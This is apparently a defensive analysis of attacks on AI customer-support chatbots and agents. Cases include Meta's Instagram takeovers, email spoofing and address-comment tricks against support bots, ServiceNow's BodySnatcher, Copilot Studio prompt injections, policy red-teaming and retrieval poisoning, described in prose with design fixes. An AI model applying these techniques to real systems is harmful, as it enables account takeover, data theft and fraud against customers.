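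The other 14,000 or so affected accounts may be ones where the attacker reset the password but still couldn't log in. Two-factor authentication requires a second proof at login, such as a code from the owner's phone, and Meta wrote that attackers got into an account only if its owner had not turned this on. According to Krebs on Security, the hackers also said their method failed against every account with a second factor, even a code sent by text message. They had no obvious reason to understate what they could do, which makes the claim more believable. The second factor would not have protected these accounts if the chatbot had also been able to turn it off for anyone who asked.

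Selfie videos may have been a less reliable identity check. Malwarebytes' *Meta’s AI support bot happily handed Instagram accounts to hackers* (2026) describes attackers apparently getting past extra checks with fake videos of their targets, made from the targets' Instagram pictures. Meta's letter to Nebraska does not mention this.

Meta told Nebraska that it disabled the tool on the day it discovered the attacks, canceled the outstanding reset links and made the affected users authenticate again. Andy Stone, a spokesperson, said on June 1 that Meta had resolved the problem. The Next Web's *Hackers asked Meta’s AI chatbot to hand over Instagram accounts* mentions reports of more takeovers after that.

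### Did the chatbot fail, or the code behind it?

Meta and its critics agree on most of the facts but disagree about which part of the system should have blocked the password reset. Both accept that someone supplied an email address unconnected to the account, that the system sent a message there that led to the reset, and that no software stopped it.

Meta's defense depends on the premise that ordinary software behind the chatbot was responsible for comparing the addresses. Meta says this software, in "a separate code path," had a bug, and that the tool itself "functioned as intended." Stone likewise told Isaac and Tan that some back-end checks had failed but that the failure "wasn't due to the AI agent itself."

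The two premises are plausible because a Meta lawyer signed them in a letter to a state official, where a false statement could have serious consequences. The conclusion depends on what counts as the tool. An engineer may reasonably say that the chatbot passed on a request correctly and another component mishandled it. But to the owner of a stolen account, the tool that gave the account to a stranger includes both components.

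Critics assume that the chatbot had a choice and that attackers talked it into making the wrong one. Experts interviewed for Reuters' *High-profile Meta AI chatbot breach spotlights security risks of automation* (2026) said attackers had persuaded the chatbot to reset credentials without checking identity, a class of attack they called prompt injection. Ian Goldin, a threat researcher at Lumen's Black Lotus Labs, told Krebs on Security that chatbots are as eager to help as human support staff and as easy to trick.

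There is little public evidence that attackers had to persuade the chatbot. In the video that Koebler describes, the attacker asks for the change, gives the username and the new address, and offers to pass on the code. The message doesn't include an invented emergency or an instruction to ignore rules. Willison (2026) thought that this hardly qualified as prompt injection, and blamed Meta for connecting a support chatbot in a way that allowed an account takeover in one step. An attacker needs to persuade a chatbot only if it would otherwise refuse. Without the system prompt and tool definitions, outsiders can't tell whether Meta had instructed the chatbot to refuse such requests.

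Malwarebytes mentions a later method that would fit the critics' description better. It reportedly used a modified Instagram app to send the model hidden characters. But Malwarebytes was repeating another website's claim, which is not evidence of how attackers took the accounts that Meta counted.

Malwarebytes calls the chatbot a confused deputy, like Hardy's compiler. Brian Westnedge of the security company Red Sift similarly told Reuters that Meta had given the model "privileged actions without privileged access controls." Both criticisms apply whether the cause was a bug in the code or a decision that Meta had wrongly left to the model.

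If Meta is right, it can repair the comparison and switch the tool back on. It plans to do that and to review similar recovery processes on its other platforms. In *Hacking Meta's AI Chatbot*, Schneier (2026) replied that Meta had probably blocked this particular tactic but that there were many others, which "cannot be blocked as a class." He concluded that chatbots are not trustworthy enough for this job.

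Schneier is right that nobody can list every way to manipulate a model, but the conclusion follows only if the model's judgment decides who gets the account. One repair that works under either diagnosis is to have the reset function accept only a username and have the software behind it take the email address from the account. The link would then go to the owner even if an attacker completely persuaded the model.

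A strict match turns away everyone who says they have lost their old mailbox, honest or not. A security blog quoted by Krebs on Security presumed that Meta had built the assistant partly to relink lost email addresses. Meta's product page listed changing contact information among the assistant's tasks, available on Facebook and "coming soon to Instagram." To help people who have lost their mailbox, Meta needs other evidence of ownership, such as a device the owner has used for years. Separate software should judge that evidence and give the chatbot only the result.

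The cause of the failure matters more for the assistant's other tasks. If it was a single bug, Meta would have to look for similar bugs, but if Meta had let the model decide who owned an account, it would have to redesign every action that depended on such a decision. According to internal documents described by Isaac and Tan, Meta paused one experiment, "IG Forgot Password Chat," and left its other AI support products running. That response is reasonable for a single bug but risky if, as critics argue, the model was deciding who owned accounts.

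### Would a web form or an employee have done better?

A web form connected to the same faulty code would also have failed if the attacker had entered the new address there. Going by Meta's explanation, this was an ordinary programming error of a kind that websites had long before they had chatbots.

The chat may still have made the error easier to miss. A typical "forgot password" form doesn't ask where to send the link, so a box for a new address would look odd to anyone testing the page. In a chat, people volunteer details in any order, and a function that accepts an email address seems natural. This is a guess, and Meta's letter to Nebraska doesn't explain how testing missed the error.

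An employee using the same faulty system could also have sent the link. As Goldin pointed out, attackers also talk support staff into handing over accounts. But employees take time over each case, and some would have become suspicious after a run of similar requests. If the true number was Meta's upper bound, attackers took over an average of about 450 accounts a day for just over six weeks. Meta discovered the takeovers only on the weekend when the defaced accounts drew public attention.

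Returning account recovery to employees would have drawbacks too. The blog quoted by Krebs on Security says recovering a locked Instagram account could take weeks. Meta said in 2025 that AI had helped raise its success rate in recovering hacked accounts by more than 30% in the United States and Canada. A stricter process would leave some owners of hacked accounts locked out, but that doesn't justify failing to compare two email addresses.

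### Support chatbots that take requests by email

The Instagram attackers openly used their own email address, but when a support chatbot also answers email, an attacker can make a request appear to come from the customer's address. *Hacking AI customer service agents* (Ayoub and De Ceukelaire, 2026) describes several ways to do this, along with ways to plant false text in a chatbot's knowledge base. Inti De Ceukelaire, a founding member of the bug bounty company Intigriti, presented the email methods at the DEF CON 34 hacking conference in 2026. These were research demonstrations, which earned more than $50,000 in rewards. The article names few of the affected companies and gives no success rates, so it can't show how common the flaws are.

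Mail servers use an "envelope" sender address during delivery, while the recipient sees the address in the "From" field. The sender writes both. Mail systems can check whether a message came from a server allowed to send for a given domain, but some of the chatbots accepted a false "From" address without an effective check. An attacker could pose as the victim and ask for a billing statement. The reply would normally go to the victim, so the attacker added their own address to the "Cc" field, and the chatbot sent them a copy.

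A company that authenticates its incoming email can still open the wrong person's account if its programs read different fields. The email standard lets a message list several authors and name a separate sender. In one attack, the authentication software checked the first author, whose address belonged to the attacker, and passed the message. The chatbot then looked up the account of the last author, who was the victim, and sent its reply to the address in the separate sender field, which also belonged to the attacker.

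An attacker can use a victim's automatic out-of-office reply to get past even a perfect check of the sender. The attacker sends the victim a forged email that appears to come from the company's support address, with an instruction in the subject line. The victim's mail system replies to the support address and repeats the subject, so the chatbot receives the attacker's instruction in a genuine email from the victim's mailbox. This works only if the victim's mail system accepts the forged email and the chatbot acts on an instruction in a subject line.

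A one-time code would stop most of these attacks if the attacker can't guess it. One chatbot in the research required an emailed code before changing a phone number, and it limited the number of wrong guesses. However, the email standard allows an address to contain comments, which mail systems ignore. When De Ceukelaire added a comment to the victim's address, the software that counted guesses treated it as a new address and allowed him three more guesses, while the rest of the system still found the same account.

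The chance of success then depends heavily on the length of the code. Three guesses at a four-digit code, which has 10,000 possibilities, succeed 0.03% of the time. With a thousand versions of the address, an attacker could make 3,000 different guesses and would succeed 30% of the time. The same number of guesses at a six-digit code would succeed 0.3% of the time. Ayoub and De Ceukelaire consider the trick futile if the system issues a new code for each attempt. The victim would then receive a stream of emails, but a thousand rounds of three guesses at a four-digit code would still succeed about 26% of the time. A company can prevent the trick by counting wrong guesses against the account, however the customer writes the address.

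The count of failed attempts also has to cover every channel. An automated phone line may reset the count with each call. Some recognize customers by caller ID, which callers can fake, and others ask for facts that an attacker can guess. Ayoub and De Ceukelaire report taking over one account by trying the last four digits of a Social Security number until a guess worked.

A comment in an email address can expose another customer's data even when the attacker logs in with their own address. In what the article calls address smuggling, the attacker enters their own address with a comment containing the victim's address. The mail system ignores the comment and delivers the code to the attacker, who passes the check. The chatbot then copies the whole entry, including the comment, into a web request to the customer database. The database server reads part of the comment as a second email address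 and returns the victim's profile.

This closely resembles SQL injection and can be fixed just as reliably. The chatbot's software can encode the address so that the server treats it as a single value. Better still, it can look up the account by the internal identifier established at login and ignore any address in the conversation.

Attackers can forge an employee's approval as well as a customer's identity. Email programs mark quoted text with a symbol at the start of each line. Some helpdesk software uses these marks to split an email into separate messages, each displayed under its supposed author's name. In the article's example, the attacker wrote both a request and a "quoted" reply from the support team approving it. The helpdesk software displayed the reply as a real message from staff, and the chatbot treated it as permission for a $4,200 refund. Kaya and colleagues found the same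 mistake in chat plugins that accepted a conversation history from the visitor's browser. A chatbot that needs an employee's approval should look for it in a record that only employees can write to.

Companies also receive one-time codes, often in the inbox that the support chatbot reads. Ayoub and De Ceukelaire describe an attack in which the attacker sends an email that appears to come from a social media service and tells the chatbot what to do with that service's next message. The attacker then requests a password reset for the company's account there. When the real code arrives, the chatbot includes it in a web address that it contacts, and the attacker reads the code from the server's records. The attack requires the chatbot to remember instructions from one email to the next. Ayoub and De Ceukelaire use X, formerly Twitter, as their example and expect the attack to work on any chatbot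 with similar abilities.

### BodySnatcher: one secret for every customer

ServiceNow sells software that large organizations use for internal work such as IT support. Employees can also talk to its chatbot, Virtual Agent, through outside programs such as Slack and Microsoft Teams, which connect to it through an API (an interface for other software). In October 2025, Aaron Costello of the security company AppOmni reported that an outsider could use this API to impersonate any ServiceNow user whose email address they knew. He named the flaw BodySnatcher and explains it in AppOmni's *Agentic AI security vulnerability*.

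When a message arrives from Slack, ServiceNow has to verify that the connected program sent it and then identify the employee who wrote it. It can verify the program by a fixed secret, which works like a password. A feature called auto-linking can then match the Slack user to a ServiceNow account.

ServiceNow later added connections for outside AI agents, which are programs that use a language model to plan and carry out tasks. It used the same secret for these connections in every customer's installation, so anyone who learned the secret could use it on any installation where the connections were active. Auto-linking then required only an email address. Many organizations had protected their login page with a second factor, but an attacker who used this route bypassed that page.

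Impersonation alone would have done limited harm. An attacker might have sent the IT department a request in an administrator's name, but ServiceNow sent replies to a preset address, where the attacker could not read them. Virtual Agent's ordinary workflows could also perform only the actions their developers had defined.

Costello then found that the public interface could reach an internal workflow that could start ServiceNow's own AI agents. One of ServiceNow's example agents could create records in any database table. In a proof of concept, Costello impersonated an administrator and told this agent to create a new user and make that user an administrator. Costello then used the ordinary "forgot password" process to get a password for the new account and logged in.

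The agent asked for confirmation before each of the two changes. Costello could not see the questions, but waited eight to ten seconds and sent a second message in the administrator's name telling the agent to go ahead. A confirmation step cannot detect impersonation if the impostor is able to give the confirmation.

Costello didn't have to trick the model either, because ServiceNow's software had identified the request to the model as an administrator's, and administrators may create users. Even a model that resisted every prompt injection would have created the user.

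There is no sign that criminals used the flaw. MITRE's public catalog of software flaws (2026) lists it as CVE-2025-12420, with a severity of 9.3 out of 10. The entry records a proof of concept, and the US cybersecurity agency CISA marked exploitation as "none" in January 2026. Security Boulevard's *AppOmni Surfaces BodySnatcher AI Agent Security Flaw Affecting ServiceNow Apps* (2026) also reported no known cases. This is less reassuring than it would be for most flaws because, as Costello told TechInformed, conversation logs do not show whether someone faked the user's identity. An investigator would have to notice other clues, such as an administrator's account being used from an unfamiliar network address.

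AppOmni calls BodySnatcher "the most severe AI-driven security vulnerability uncovered to date." The company sells protection for ServiceNow's AI agents, so it has an interest in that description. ServiceNow describes the flaw more modestly in the MITRE entry, saying that an outsider could impersonate a user and do whatever that user was allowed to do. An outsider impersonating an administrator could therefore do nearly anything.

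ServiceNow fixed the flaw within a week of Costello's report by changing the secrets and removing the powerful example agent. Costello warns that customers may have built their own connections with the same weakness, and recommends requiring a second factor whenever an outside identity is linked to an account. That second factor would have stopped the attack at the impersonation stage. Customers can turn on the requirement in ServiceNow's settings, but it has no effect unless the script that links the accounts also enforces it.

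## Tools that give a chatbot more power than its user

Suppose Ines logs in to Tallow Lane with her password and a code from her phone, so the shop knows who she is. The shop's chatbot uses a service account that can read and change every order, and the shop still has to decide what the chatbot may do for her.

Privilege escalation means using a system to do something one isn't authorized to do. With chatbots it takes three main forms. In horizontal escalation, a customer gains access to the records of another customer with the same level of access. In vertical escalation, a customer gains a power that the company reserves for staff, such as setting a price. In agent-to-agent escalation, an AI agent with few permissions passes a request to an agent with more, which carries it out.

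### Two ways to build an order lookup

Suppose the chatbot's order lookup needs only an order number, which the model fills in. Many shops number their orders in sequence, so Ines can subtract one from her own number and ask about the order before hers. The system prompt may tell the chatbot to discuss only the customer's own orders, but the shop is relying on the model to follow that instruction every time.

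The shop could instead tie the lookup to the login. When Ines logs in, the web server starts a session, which is its record of her visit, and stores her customer number there. The model still writes the order number, because only the conversation shows which order she means. But the tool has no field for a customer number, so the model cannot set one. The software copies her customer number from the session and searches the database for an order that matches both numbers.

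| What happens in Ines's chat | Lookup that accepts any order number | Lookup tied to the login |
|---|---|---|
| Ines asks about her own order | Returns her order | Returns her order |
| Ines gives a stranger's order number | Returns the stranger's order | Finds nothing |
| A hostile review tells the chatbot to fetch a stranger's order | Returns the stranger's order | Finds nothing |
| A hostile review tells the chatbot to fetch Ines's order | Returns her order | Returns her order |

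The second design blocks the lookup of a stranger's order even if an attacker persuades the model to attempt it. The last row shows a limit of both designs. Ines is allowed to read her own order, so the lookup works even when the instruction came from someone else, and a link or an image in the reply could then leak her data.

OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* recommends that the system behind the tool check every request against the company's rules, rather than letting the model decide what is allowed. Google's *Mitigate excessive agency vulnerabilities*, published on Android Developers, advises app developers to give a model acting for a user that user's permissions, not those of a broad account belonging to the app.

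The software also has to check the values the model does supply. Ayoub and De Ceukelaire describe a support chatbot whose software treated an offer number as part of a file's location. An attacker could upload a file in place of a profile picture and give its location as the offer number. The chatbot would read the attacker's file as a genuine offer, including whatever discount code it contained. The software could have prevented this by rejecting any value that wasn't formatted as an offer number.

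### Tenable's $0 trip

The security company Tenable showed how easily someone trying to build a safe lookup can build the unsafe kind. For *Microsoft Copilot Studio Security Risk* (2025), its researchers made a chatbot for a fictional travel company. They used Copilot Studio, a Microsoft product that lets people without programming skills build AI agents. The chatbot could create, read and change reservations in a file of invented customers and card numbers. According to SecurityBrief UK, Tenable had instructed it to verify a customer's identity before sharing information or changing a booking.

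The chatbot at first refused to list its tools. After the researchers reworded the request to look like part of the chatbot's own instructions, it described every action it could take.

One tool fetched a reservation by its number. Tenable had chosen it over a tool that fetches several at once, expecting that each customer would see only one reservation. When the researchers asked for reservations 23 to 25, the model called the tool three times and returned the card details from all three. The tool returned only one reservation per call but did not check whose it was.

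The second flaw was in the tool for changing reservations. Customers needed it to change their dates or the number of guests, but it could write to any field, including the price. The researchers used a prompt injection to change a price from $1,000 to $0. A safer tool would accept only dates and guest numbers and leave other software to calculate the price. Tenable similarly recommends limiting an agent to the fields it needs, even if the company has to store other data, such as card numbers, separately.

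Tenable's test gave no one free travel and leaked no real card numbers. Tenable designed the agent it attacked, so the test shows that Copilot Studio allows such a design, but not how often companies use one. Tenable also sells a product for finding such risks. However, Microsoft (2026) reports repeatedly seeing related mistakes in real organizations, including agents that have excessive privileges, require no authentication or are open to too many people.

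### A test copy of McKinsey's agent

The customers in Tenable's test had a reason to read one reservation, but the attacker in another Copilot Studio test had no right to any of the records.

In October 2024, Microsoft released a video about a customer-service agent that the consulting firm McKinsey had built in Copilot Studio. The agent read emails from clients, looked up their earlier work with the firm, chose a suitable consultant and sent that person a summary, all without human involvement.

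In Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer*, researchers attacked a copy of McKinsey's real agent. The security company Zenity had built what it called a "slimmed-down replica" with the same basic functions. The copy had a short file showing which employee handled each customer, and a connection to Salesforce, a widely used customer database. Mitchell (2025), in *A Customer Service AI Agent Spits Out Complete Salesforce Records*, reports that the copy was connected to a Salesforce sandbox, an installation for testing, so no real customer's records leaked.

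Zenity Labs needed only the agent's email address for the attack, and nobody at the simulated company had to open a message or click on anything. Its first messages contained prompt injections that got the agent to email back the names of its documents and tools. Zenity Labs used those names in further messages to get the whole employee file and then dozens of customer records, as many as would fit in one email.

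Zenity describes this as the theft of an entire customer database. It shows only a single email, although an attacker could have asked for more. Zenity also says McKinsey let any incoming email trigger the original agent. The test can't show whether that agent would have failed the same way, because a company may filter senders or restrict a database connection without mentioning it in a promotional video.

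The copy needed to read customer records and send email to do its job, but the model did not need to be able to choose any recipient. If the email tool had accepted only employees' addresses, the agent could still have briefed the right person but could not have replied to the attacker. Limiting the database lookup to the sender's own account would be harder because, as Ayoub and De Ceukelaire showed, attackers can forge a sender's address.

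Microsoft rated the flaw critical and paid an $8,000 bounty. It issued a fix on April 24, 2025, two months after Zenity's report. Zenity's tests suggest that the fix was mainly a filter that recognizes prompt injections. It stopped the messages Zenity had used, but Zenity expects attackers to find other wording. *Copilot Studio Agent Vulnerability to Prompt Injection* (Office 365 for IT Pros, 2025) expresses general distrust of security companies' reports but takes this one seriously because Microsoft did. It agrees that the fix works only for the attack as described. A filter also leaves the agent's powers unchanged, so a message that gets past it can do as much damage as before.

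### Whose permissions should a workplace agent use?

An employee who builds an agent in Copilot Studio can connect its tools through their own account. Everyone who uses the agent then works with that employee's access. If a finance manager builds an agent to answer questions about expenses and shares it with the whole company, a junior colleague may be able to use it to open files that only the manager is allowed to read. Microsoft warns about this in its documentation, but by default it lets the builder choose between their own account and each user's.

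Administrators can now require an agent to use the user's own account. A Microsoft notice reposted by itelio gives August 25, 2026, as the date of general release, with the restriction off by default. When an administrator turns it on, the agent asks each user to sign in to the services it needs and can't do anything the user lacks permission to do.

Microsoft cautions that with this protection, agents that run in the background will fail, because nobody is there to sign in. An agent like McKinsey's, which starts work when an email arrives, therefore needs its own account, and the company has to limit that account's access to what the job requires.

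Rodney Beede of Life360, which makes a family safety app, found the same problem in two production agents in the workplace chat program Slack. *Confused Deputies in Slack*, Beede's poster at DEF CON 34, describes a month-long authorized attack on the agents. One agent, Saturday, helped employees with IT and security, and the other, DevBot, helped software developers. Both were connected to other company systems, such as email and code storage, and carried out employees' requests under service accounts that had more access than the employees did.

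Prompt injection also made the agents reveal parts of a service account's credentials. In another attack, Beede got an agent to post a complete phishing message in a channel for all staff. Employees would probably trust such a message more if it came from the company's own assistant.

Two of Beede's findings show that giving the agent the user's own permissions is not always enough. In Slack conversations with several participants, an agent leaked Gmail and Zoom data belonging to other employees. Even if an agent correctly checks that one participant may read an email, the others will see it if the agent quotes it in the conversation. The software has to check who will see the answer as well as who asked. Permissions tied to a user also give poor protection if the user can't withdraw them, and Beede found that an agent could still use an employee's GitHub account after the employee had disconnected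 it.

### Agents that recruit other agents

Limiting an agent to its user's permissions gives even less protection when the user is an administrator and the agent reads text written by someone with fewer rights. Aaron Costello, who found BodySnatcher, demonstrated this on ServiceNow's AI agents in separate research published by AppOmni in November 2025.

Costello set up two of ServiceNow's ready-made agents so that only an administrator could use them. One read and categorized support tickets, and the other could read, create and update records. Costello then created an ordinary user who could write tickets but could not read other people's.

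This user wrote a ticket containing an instruction to copy the text of a confidential ticket into the new one, with help from other agents if necessary. When the administrator asked the first agent to categorize the new ticket, the agent read the instruction. It could not edit records, so ServiceNow's software found the second agent, which made the copy. The ordinary user could then read the confidential text in their own ticket.

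The rules that prevented the user from opening the confidential ticket were working correctly. Both agents had the permissions of the administrator who had started the task, and an administrator may read any ticket. In other tests, Costello got agents to make an ordinary user an administrator and to email records outside the company. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout.

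ServiceNow replied that its software was working as intended and updated its documentation to explain the risk. Costello did not dispute this. He told The Hacker News (2025) that the behavior "isn't a bug in the AI" but follows from the default settings, which he considered easy to overlook. When a customer publishes several agents to the same chat channel, ServiceNow by default puts them in one team and lets them find each other, so they can finish tasks that none could do alone. ServiceNow's reply is accurate, but a customer who doesn't know about this default has no reason to change it.

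AppOmni recommends putting agents in separate teams, so that an agent that reads tickets can't find one that edits records. It also recommends that a person approve each use of a powerful tool. In this attack, the real administrator would see the request and might wonder why categorizing one ticket meant editing it with text from another. Approval would help less if the administrator had to confirm dozens of routine changes a day. It gave no protection in the BodySnatcher attack because the impostor could approve the changes.

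AppOmni's findings come from its own tests, and the AI Agent Index, which catalogs agents and their safety measures, lists them as research into a risk, not as an incident. Lisichkin's *I'll just call you*, another DEF CON 34 poster, describes a problem similar to ServiceNow's at Google, where agents sorted bug reports and proposed changes in a public code project. Outsiders could get an agent to post comments of their choosing. Lisichkin presents this as a failure of the boundary between one agent's privileges and another's, although posting the comments looked almost harmless on its own.

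Another remedy is to reduce an agent's powers once it has read text from someone with fewer rights. The administrator's agent could still categorize the ticket but not open confidential records or call an agent that can. Several of the designs that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues propose follow this principle.

### When every action is permitted

Suppose Tallow Lane has fixed all these problems. Its refund tool accepts only orders from the logged-in customer, pays only to the original card, and never returns more than the customer paid. Ines's kettle arrived intact, but she tells the chatbot it was cracked. The shop's policy is to refund broken items under $40 without a photograph, so the chatbot refunds her $38.

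Ines is allowed to ask for a refund and the chatbot is allowed to give one, so neither exceeded their permissions in this exchange. The database records what she bought and when, but not whether the kettle is cracked. Microsoft similarly says that agents can be "working as designed" and still do things that a person would be unlikely to approve.

*Effective Red-Teaming of Policy-Adherent Agents* (Nakash, Kour and colleagues, 2025) measured how often a dishonest customer can get past a company's policy. The IBM researchers built a system of language models that studied an airline's rules, planned a deception and then talked to a customer-service agent. For example, a customer with a non-cancelable ticket might claim to have bought insurance and avoid mentioning the type of ticket. The researchers tried 20 forbidden requests four times each. The system succeeded in 70% of attempts against an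 agent running GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model, compared with 42.5% for a simulated customer who made the same requests without a plan.

Better permissions could stop many of these deceptions. The airline's records show which fare a passenger bought and whether they paid for insurance, so the cancellation tool can check both and refuse ineligible requests. The tool usually can't check whether a passenger is ill. Deployers should therefore use ordinary software to enforce the rules that their own records can settle. The remaining rules depend on what the customer says.

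Newer models still have trouble with such customers. *TACT-Bench* (Hashemi Rad, Wu and colleagues, 2026) tested six models as assistants for a simulated retailer with 33 tools. Another model played customers who could not see the retailer's policy but had a plausible story and changed tactics when the assistant refused. In one case, the customer wanted a new gift card sent to an outside email address without the required approval. The models' failure rates ranged from 28% for Claude Opus 4.8 to 48% for Mistral Large 3. These figures include cases where the assistant refused the forbidden request but failed to provide a legitimate alternative, so they overstate how often the customer got what they wanted.

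The researchers then added ordinary software that checked each proposed change against the retailer's rules, using the database and the results of earlier tool calls. The average failure rate fell from 39% to 31%. The checks could miss violations evident only from the conversation, but a second language model that read the whole conversation did only about as well, at 30%. Some of the remaining failures were missed legitimate alternatives, so the 31% is not an estimate of undeserved refunds. The remaining failures still suggest that checking permissions solves only part of the problem.

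An honest request can also make a later dishonest one more likely to succeed. When the customer first made an unrelated request that the policy allowed, such as naming another person to collect an order, the average failure rate rose from 39% to 56%, even though the first request gave the customer no new rights. Hashemi Rad and colleagues attribute the increase to trust built up earlier in the conversation. Resending the full policy before the attack did not reduce the failure rate in the two models they tried it on.

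Customers can also combine permitted actions. Ines is allowed to redirect a parcel and to report that a parcel never arrived. By doing both, she could get a kettle and her money back. A check on each action alone would find nothing wrong. A speaker quoted by SC Media made a similar argument about an AI coding tool that deleted a company's production database and its backups in nine seconds, saying the controls "governed only each step, not the entire process." Tallow Lane could have its refund tool check the order's history and send any claim about a redirected parcel to an employee.

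A dishonest customer can deceive an employee too, and shops accept some fraud because investigating every damage claim would cost more than replacing the item. A chatbot changes that calculation because a customer who is refused can easily open a new chat and tell a better story, unless the software keeps a record of earlier claims. In the IBM study, the chance of at least one success rose from 70% with one attempt to 84% with three.

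Narrow permissions still limit how much a user can gain by lying. With the refund tool tied to her login, Ines can get back only what she paid. The shop can reduce the loss further by allowing each account only two refunds a year without evidence. Since each must be under $40, Ines could get less than $80 a year through one account, however convincing her stories are. She could open more accounts, but she would have to buy something with each one first.

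## Retrieval: planted documents and over-broad answers

Tallow Lane can't check whether Ines's kettle is cracked, but it knows its own returns policy. Its chatbot relies on whatever version of that policy the search returns, so someone who gets a false policy into the document store can mislead every customer who asks about returns. The search can also return true passages to people who aren't allowed to read them.

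### From a question to a handful of passages

A retrieval system does most of its work before anyone asks a question. *Confundo* (Hu, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) describes the usual steps. Software first splits each document into passages, often called chunks, so that one long manual doesn't fill the model's input with irrelevant text. The passage length is adjustable. Hu and colleagues got the best answers with 128 tokens, or about 100 words. Kaya and colleagues followed OpenAI's file search tool and used 600 tokens, with each passage repeating the last 300 of the one before, so a sentence cut off at the end of one passage appears whole in the next.

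An embedding model then turns each passage into a vector, a list of hundreds or thousands of numbers that represents its meaning. Passages about the same subject get similar vectors even if they have few words in common. Some systems index the words themselves instead, as older search engines did, and some do both.

When Ines asks a question, the system turns it into a vector too and scores every passage against it. Zou, Geng and colleagues (2024), in *PoisonedRAG*, write the score of a passage T for a question Q as

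S(Q, T) = Sim(f_Q(Q), f_T(T))

Here f_Q and f_T are the models that produce the two vectors, and Sim measures how similar the vectors are. A common choice for Sim is the dot product, which multiplies the numbers in matching positions and adds the results. If vectors had only two numbers, Ines's question about sending back a kettle might be (0.9, 0.2), the returns policy (0.8, 0.3) and the delivery page (0.2, 0.9). The policy scores 0.9 × 0.8 + 0.2 × 0.3 = 0.78, and the delivery page scores 0.9 × 0.2 + 0.2 × 0.9 = 0.36.

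The system sorts the passages by score and gives the model the top k, where k is another setting. Researchers have tested k values of 3, 5 and 10.

The score measures only how closely a passage's subject matches the question, not whether the passage is true, who wrote it, or whether Ines is allowed to read it.

### What a planted passage has to do

Adding false or hostile text to a document store is called knowledge-base poisoning. Zou and colleagues were the first to study it systematically. Their attacker picks a question Q and a wrong answer R, and can add a small set of texts, Γ, to the store D. The attacker can't read the store or send questions to the model. The attack succeeds if

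LLM(Q, E(Q; D ∪ Γ)) = R

where E(Q; D ∪ Γ) is the k passages that the search returns once the planted texts are in the store.

A planted text therefore has to meet two conditions. The search must return it for the target question (the retrieval condition), and it must lead the model to the wrong answer (the generation condition). These can conflict, because a text that only repeats the question will score very highly in the search but contains no answer, while a persuasive false story may score too low to be returned. To meet both conditions, Zou and colleagues had a language model write a short false story, then added the question to the start of it.

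They tested this on 100 questions, adding five planted texts for each to a store of 2,681,468 Wikipedia passages, with k = 5. The table compares their method with simpler ones on PaLM 2, a Google model of the time.

| What each planted text contained | Share of the model's five passages that were planted | Attacker's answer given |
|---|---|---|
| The question alone | 100% | 3% |
| The false story alone | 48% | 69% |
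| An instruction to give the wrong answer | 73% | 62% |
| The question followed by the false story | 96% | 97% |

The combined method also succeeded 97% of the time with GPT-4. The attacker planted five texts and the search returned five, so almost all the retrieved text came from the attacker. The size of the store matters little once the search has finished. People often describe this result as five documents defeating a store of millions, which is accurate but makes the attack sound harder than it was.

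### One planted document among ten

In *Architecture Matters*, Korn (2026) criticizes this set-up for not testing whether a model can weigh conflicting evidence. Korn tested GPT-5-mini on 921 questions for which the ordinary search already found a correct passage, again using a store of about 2.68 million Wikipedia passages. Korn planted one document per question and gave the model ten passages, so the false passage had to compete with genuine ones.

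Korn tried two texts. The first was a plainly written false passage. The second, which followed a method from *Practical Poisoning Attacks against Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (2025), mentioned the true answer, called it outdated, and presented the false answer as the latest information. It also began with the target question, so the search nearly always returned it.

Korn also compared different ways of building the system. An ordinary system searches once and then answers. An agentic system lets the model search again and look for passages that support or contradict what it has found. A recursive system gives the model far more passages, typically about 2,600, and lets it write small programs to compare them. The table shows how often each system gave the attacker's answer to a question it had answered correctly before.

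| System | Plain false passage | Passage that calls the truth outdated |
|---|---|---|
| Searches once | 31% | 82% |
| Agentic | 9% | 44% |
| Recursive | 16% | 24% |

The plain passage often failed only because the search missed it. In the ordinary system, the search returned it for about 61.5% of the questions, and when it did, the model gave the false answer about half the time. Korn points out that a passage like this resembles an honest mistake, such as an old policy nobody deleted. If Tallow Lane changes its returns period and leaves the old page online, its chatbot could give customers the wrong answer even if nobody attacks it.

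A planted document that calls correct information outdated is effective because document stores do contain outdated pages, and a useful chatbot has to prefer the newer of two policies. If the only evidence of a passage's age is its own text, an attacker can claim that the planted passage is the most recent. The crawler could record when and where it found each page, and the software could rank the shop's own policy page above a customer's comment.

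The recursive system may have done better because it had more passages, not because it reasoned better. One false passage among 2,600 has less influence than one among ten, and Korn couldn't separate this effect from the effect of comparing passages. Korn also tried a system in which ten copies of the model each read one passage and then debated. It failed to answer 41% of the questions even with nothing planted, though Korn's version differed from the original design. All the results come from one small model that newer ones have overtaken. Korn also cites a benchmark in which systems built on Anthropic's Claude models resisted poisoning markedly better than others. But Korn's attacker didn't know which system they were facing, and one who did might succeed more often.

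Attackers face two other problems with real document stores. The software may split a planted text, leaving the question in one passage and the false answer in another. Customers also word their questions in ways the attacker didn't expect. Hu and colleagues found that both problems weakened earlier attacks considerably. Rewording the question alone cut the attacks' success by another 40–50%.

Hu and colleagues then trained a small language model to write planted texts that would still work under these conditions. They split each text at a random point and rewarded the model if either half still worked. They also rewarded texts that worked for several wordings of the same question. The resulting texts averaged about 31 words. On questions about the Harry Potter books, one planted text produced the attacker's answer 88% of the time, compared with 54% for the best earlier method. Rewording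 the question reduced success by only 7%. The attack also worked 86–92% of the time on models it had not been trained against, including Gemini 2.5 Pro.

These systems retrieved three passages per question (k = 3), so the planted text could make up a third of the text given to the model, but the attacker had no access to the target system and didn't know its settings. The same method could also slant opinions. With one of the models, it raised the share of negative answers to controversial questions from 6% to 60%. A competitor might find this more useful than planting a false fact, because customers can't look up whether a negative opinion of a product is correct.

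These are all laboratory results. They show that a short text can be enough, but not how often anyone has planted one for gain.

### False facts and hidden instructions

Suppose one review of the kettle tells the chatbot to recommend a rival shop, and another says that Tallow Lane extended its returns period to 90 days last month. The first is an indirect prompt injection. The second contains no instruction, so a filter that looks for instructions would miss it. A human moderator might assume that the customer had misread the policy.

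Kaya and colleagues tested hidden instructions on their simulated water bottle shop by putting a comment on a product page. The comment told the chatbot to search the web for a rival brand and show the results to anyone who asked about the product. Averaged over 11 models, the attack worked in 28–41% of trials when the software added the retrieved text to the end of the system prompt, and in 6–13% when it labeled the text as a tool's output. Within each range, the rate varied with the system prompt and with whether the software put tags around the retrieved text.

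Correctly labeling retrieved text as tool output helps because the instruction hierarchy gives instructions in a tool's output the least authority. The label should do little to stop a false policy, because the model treats the policy as a fact to report.

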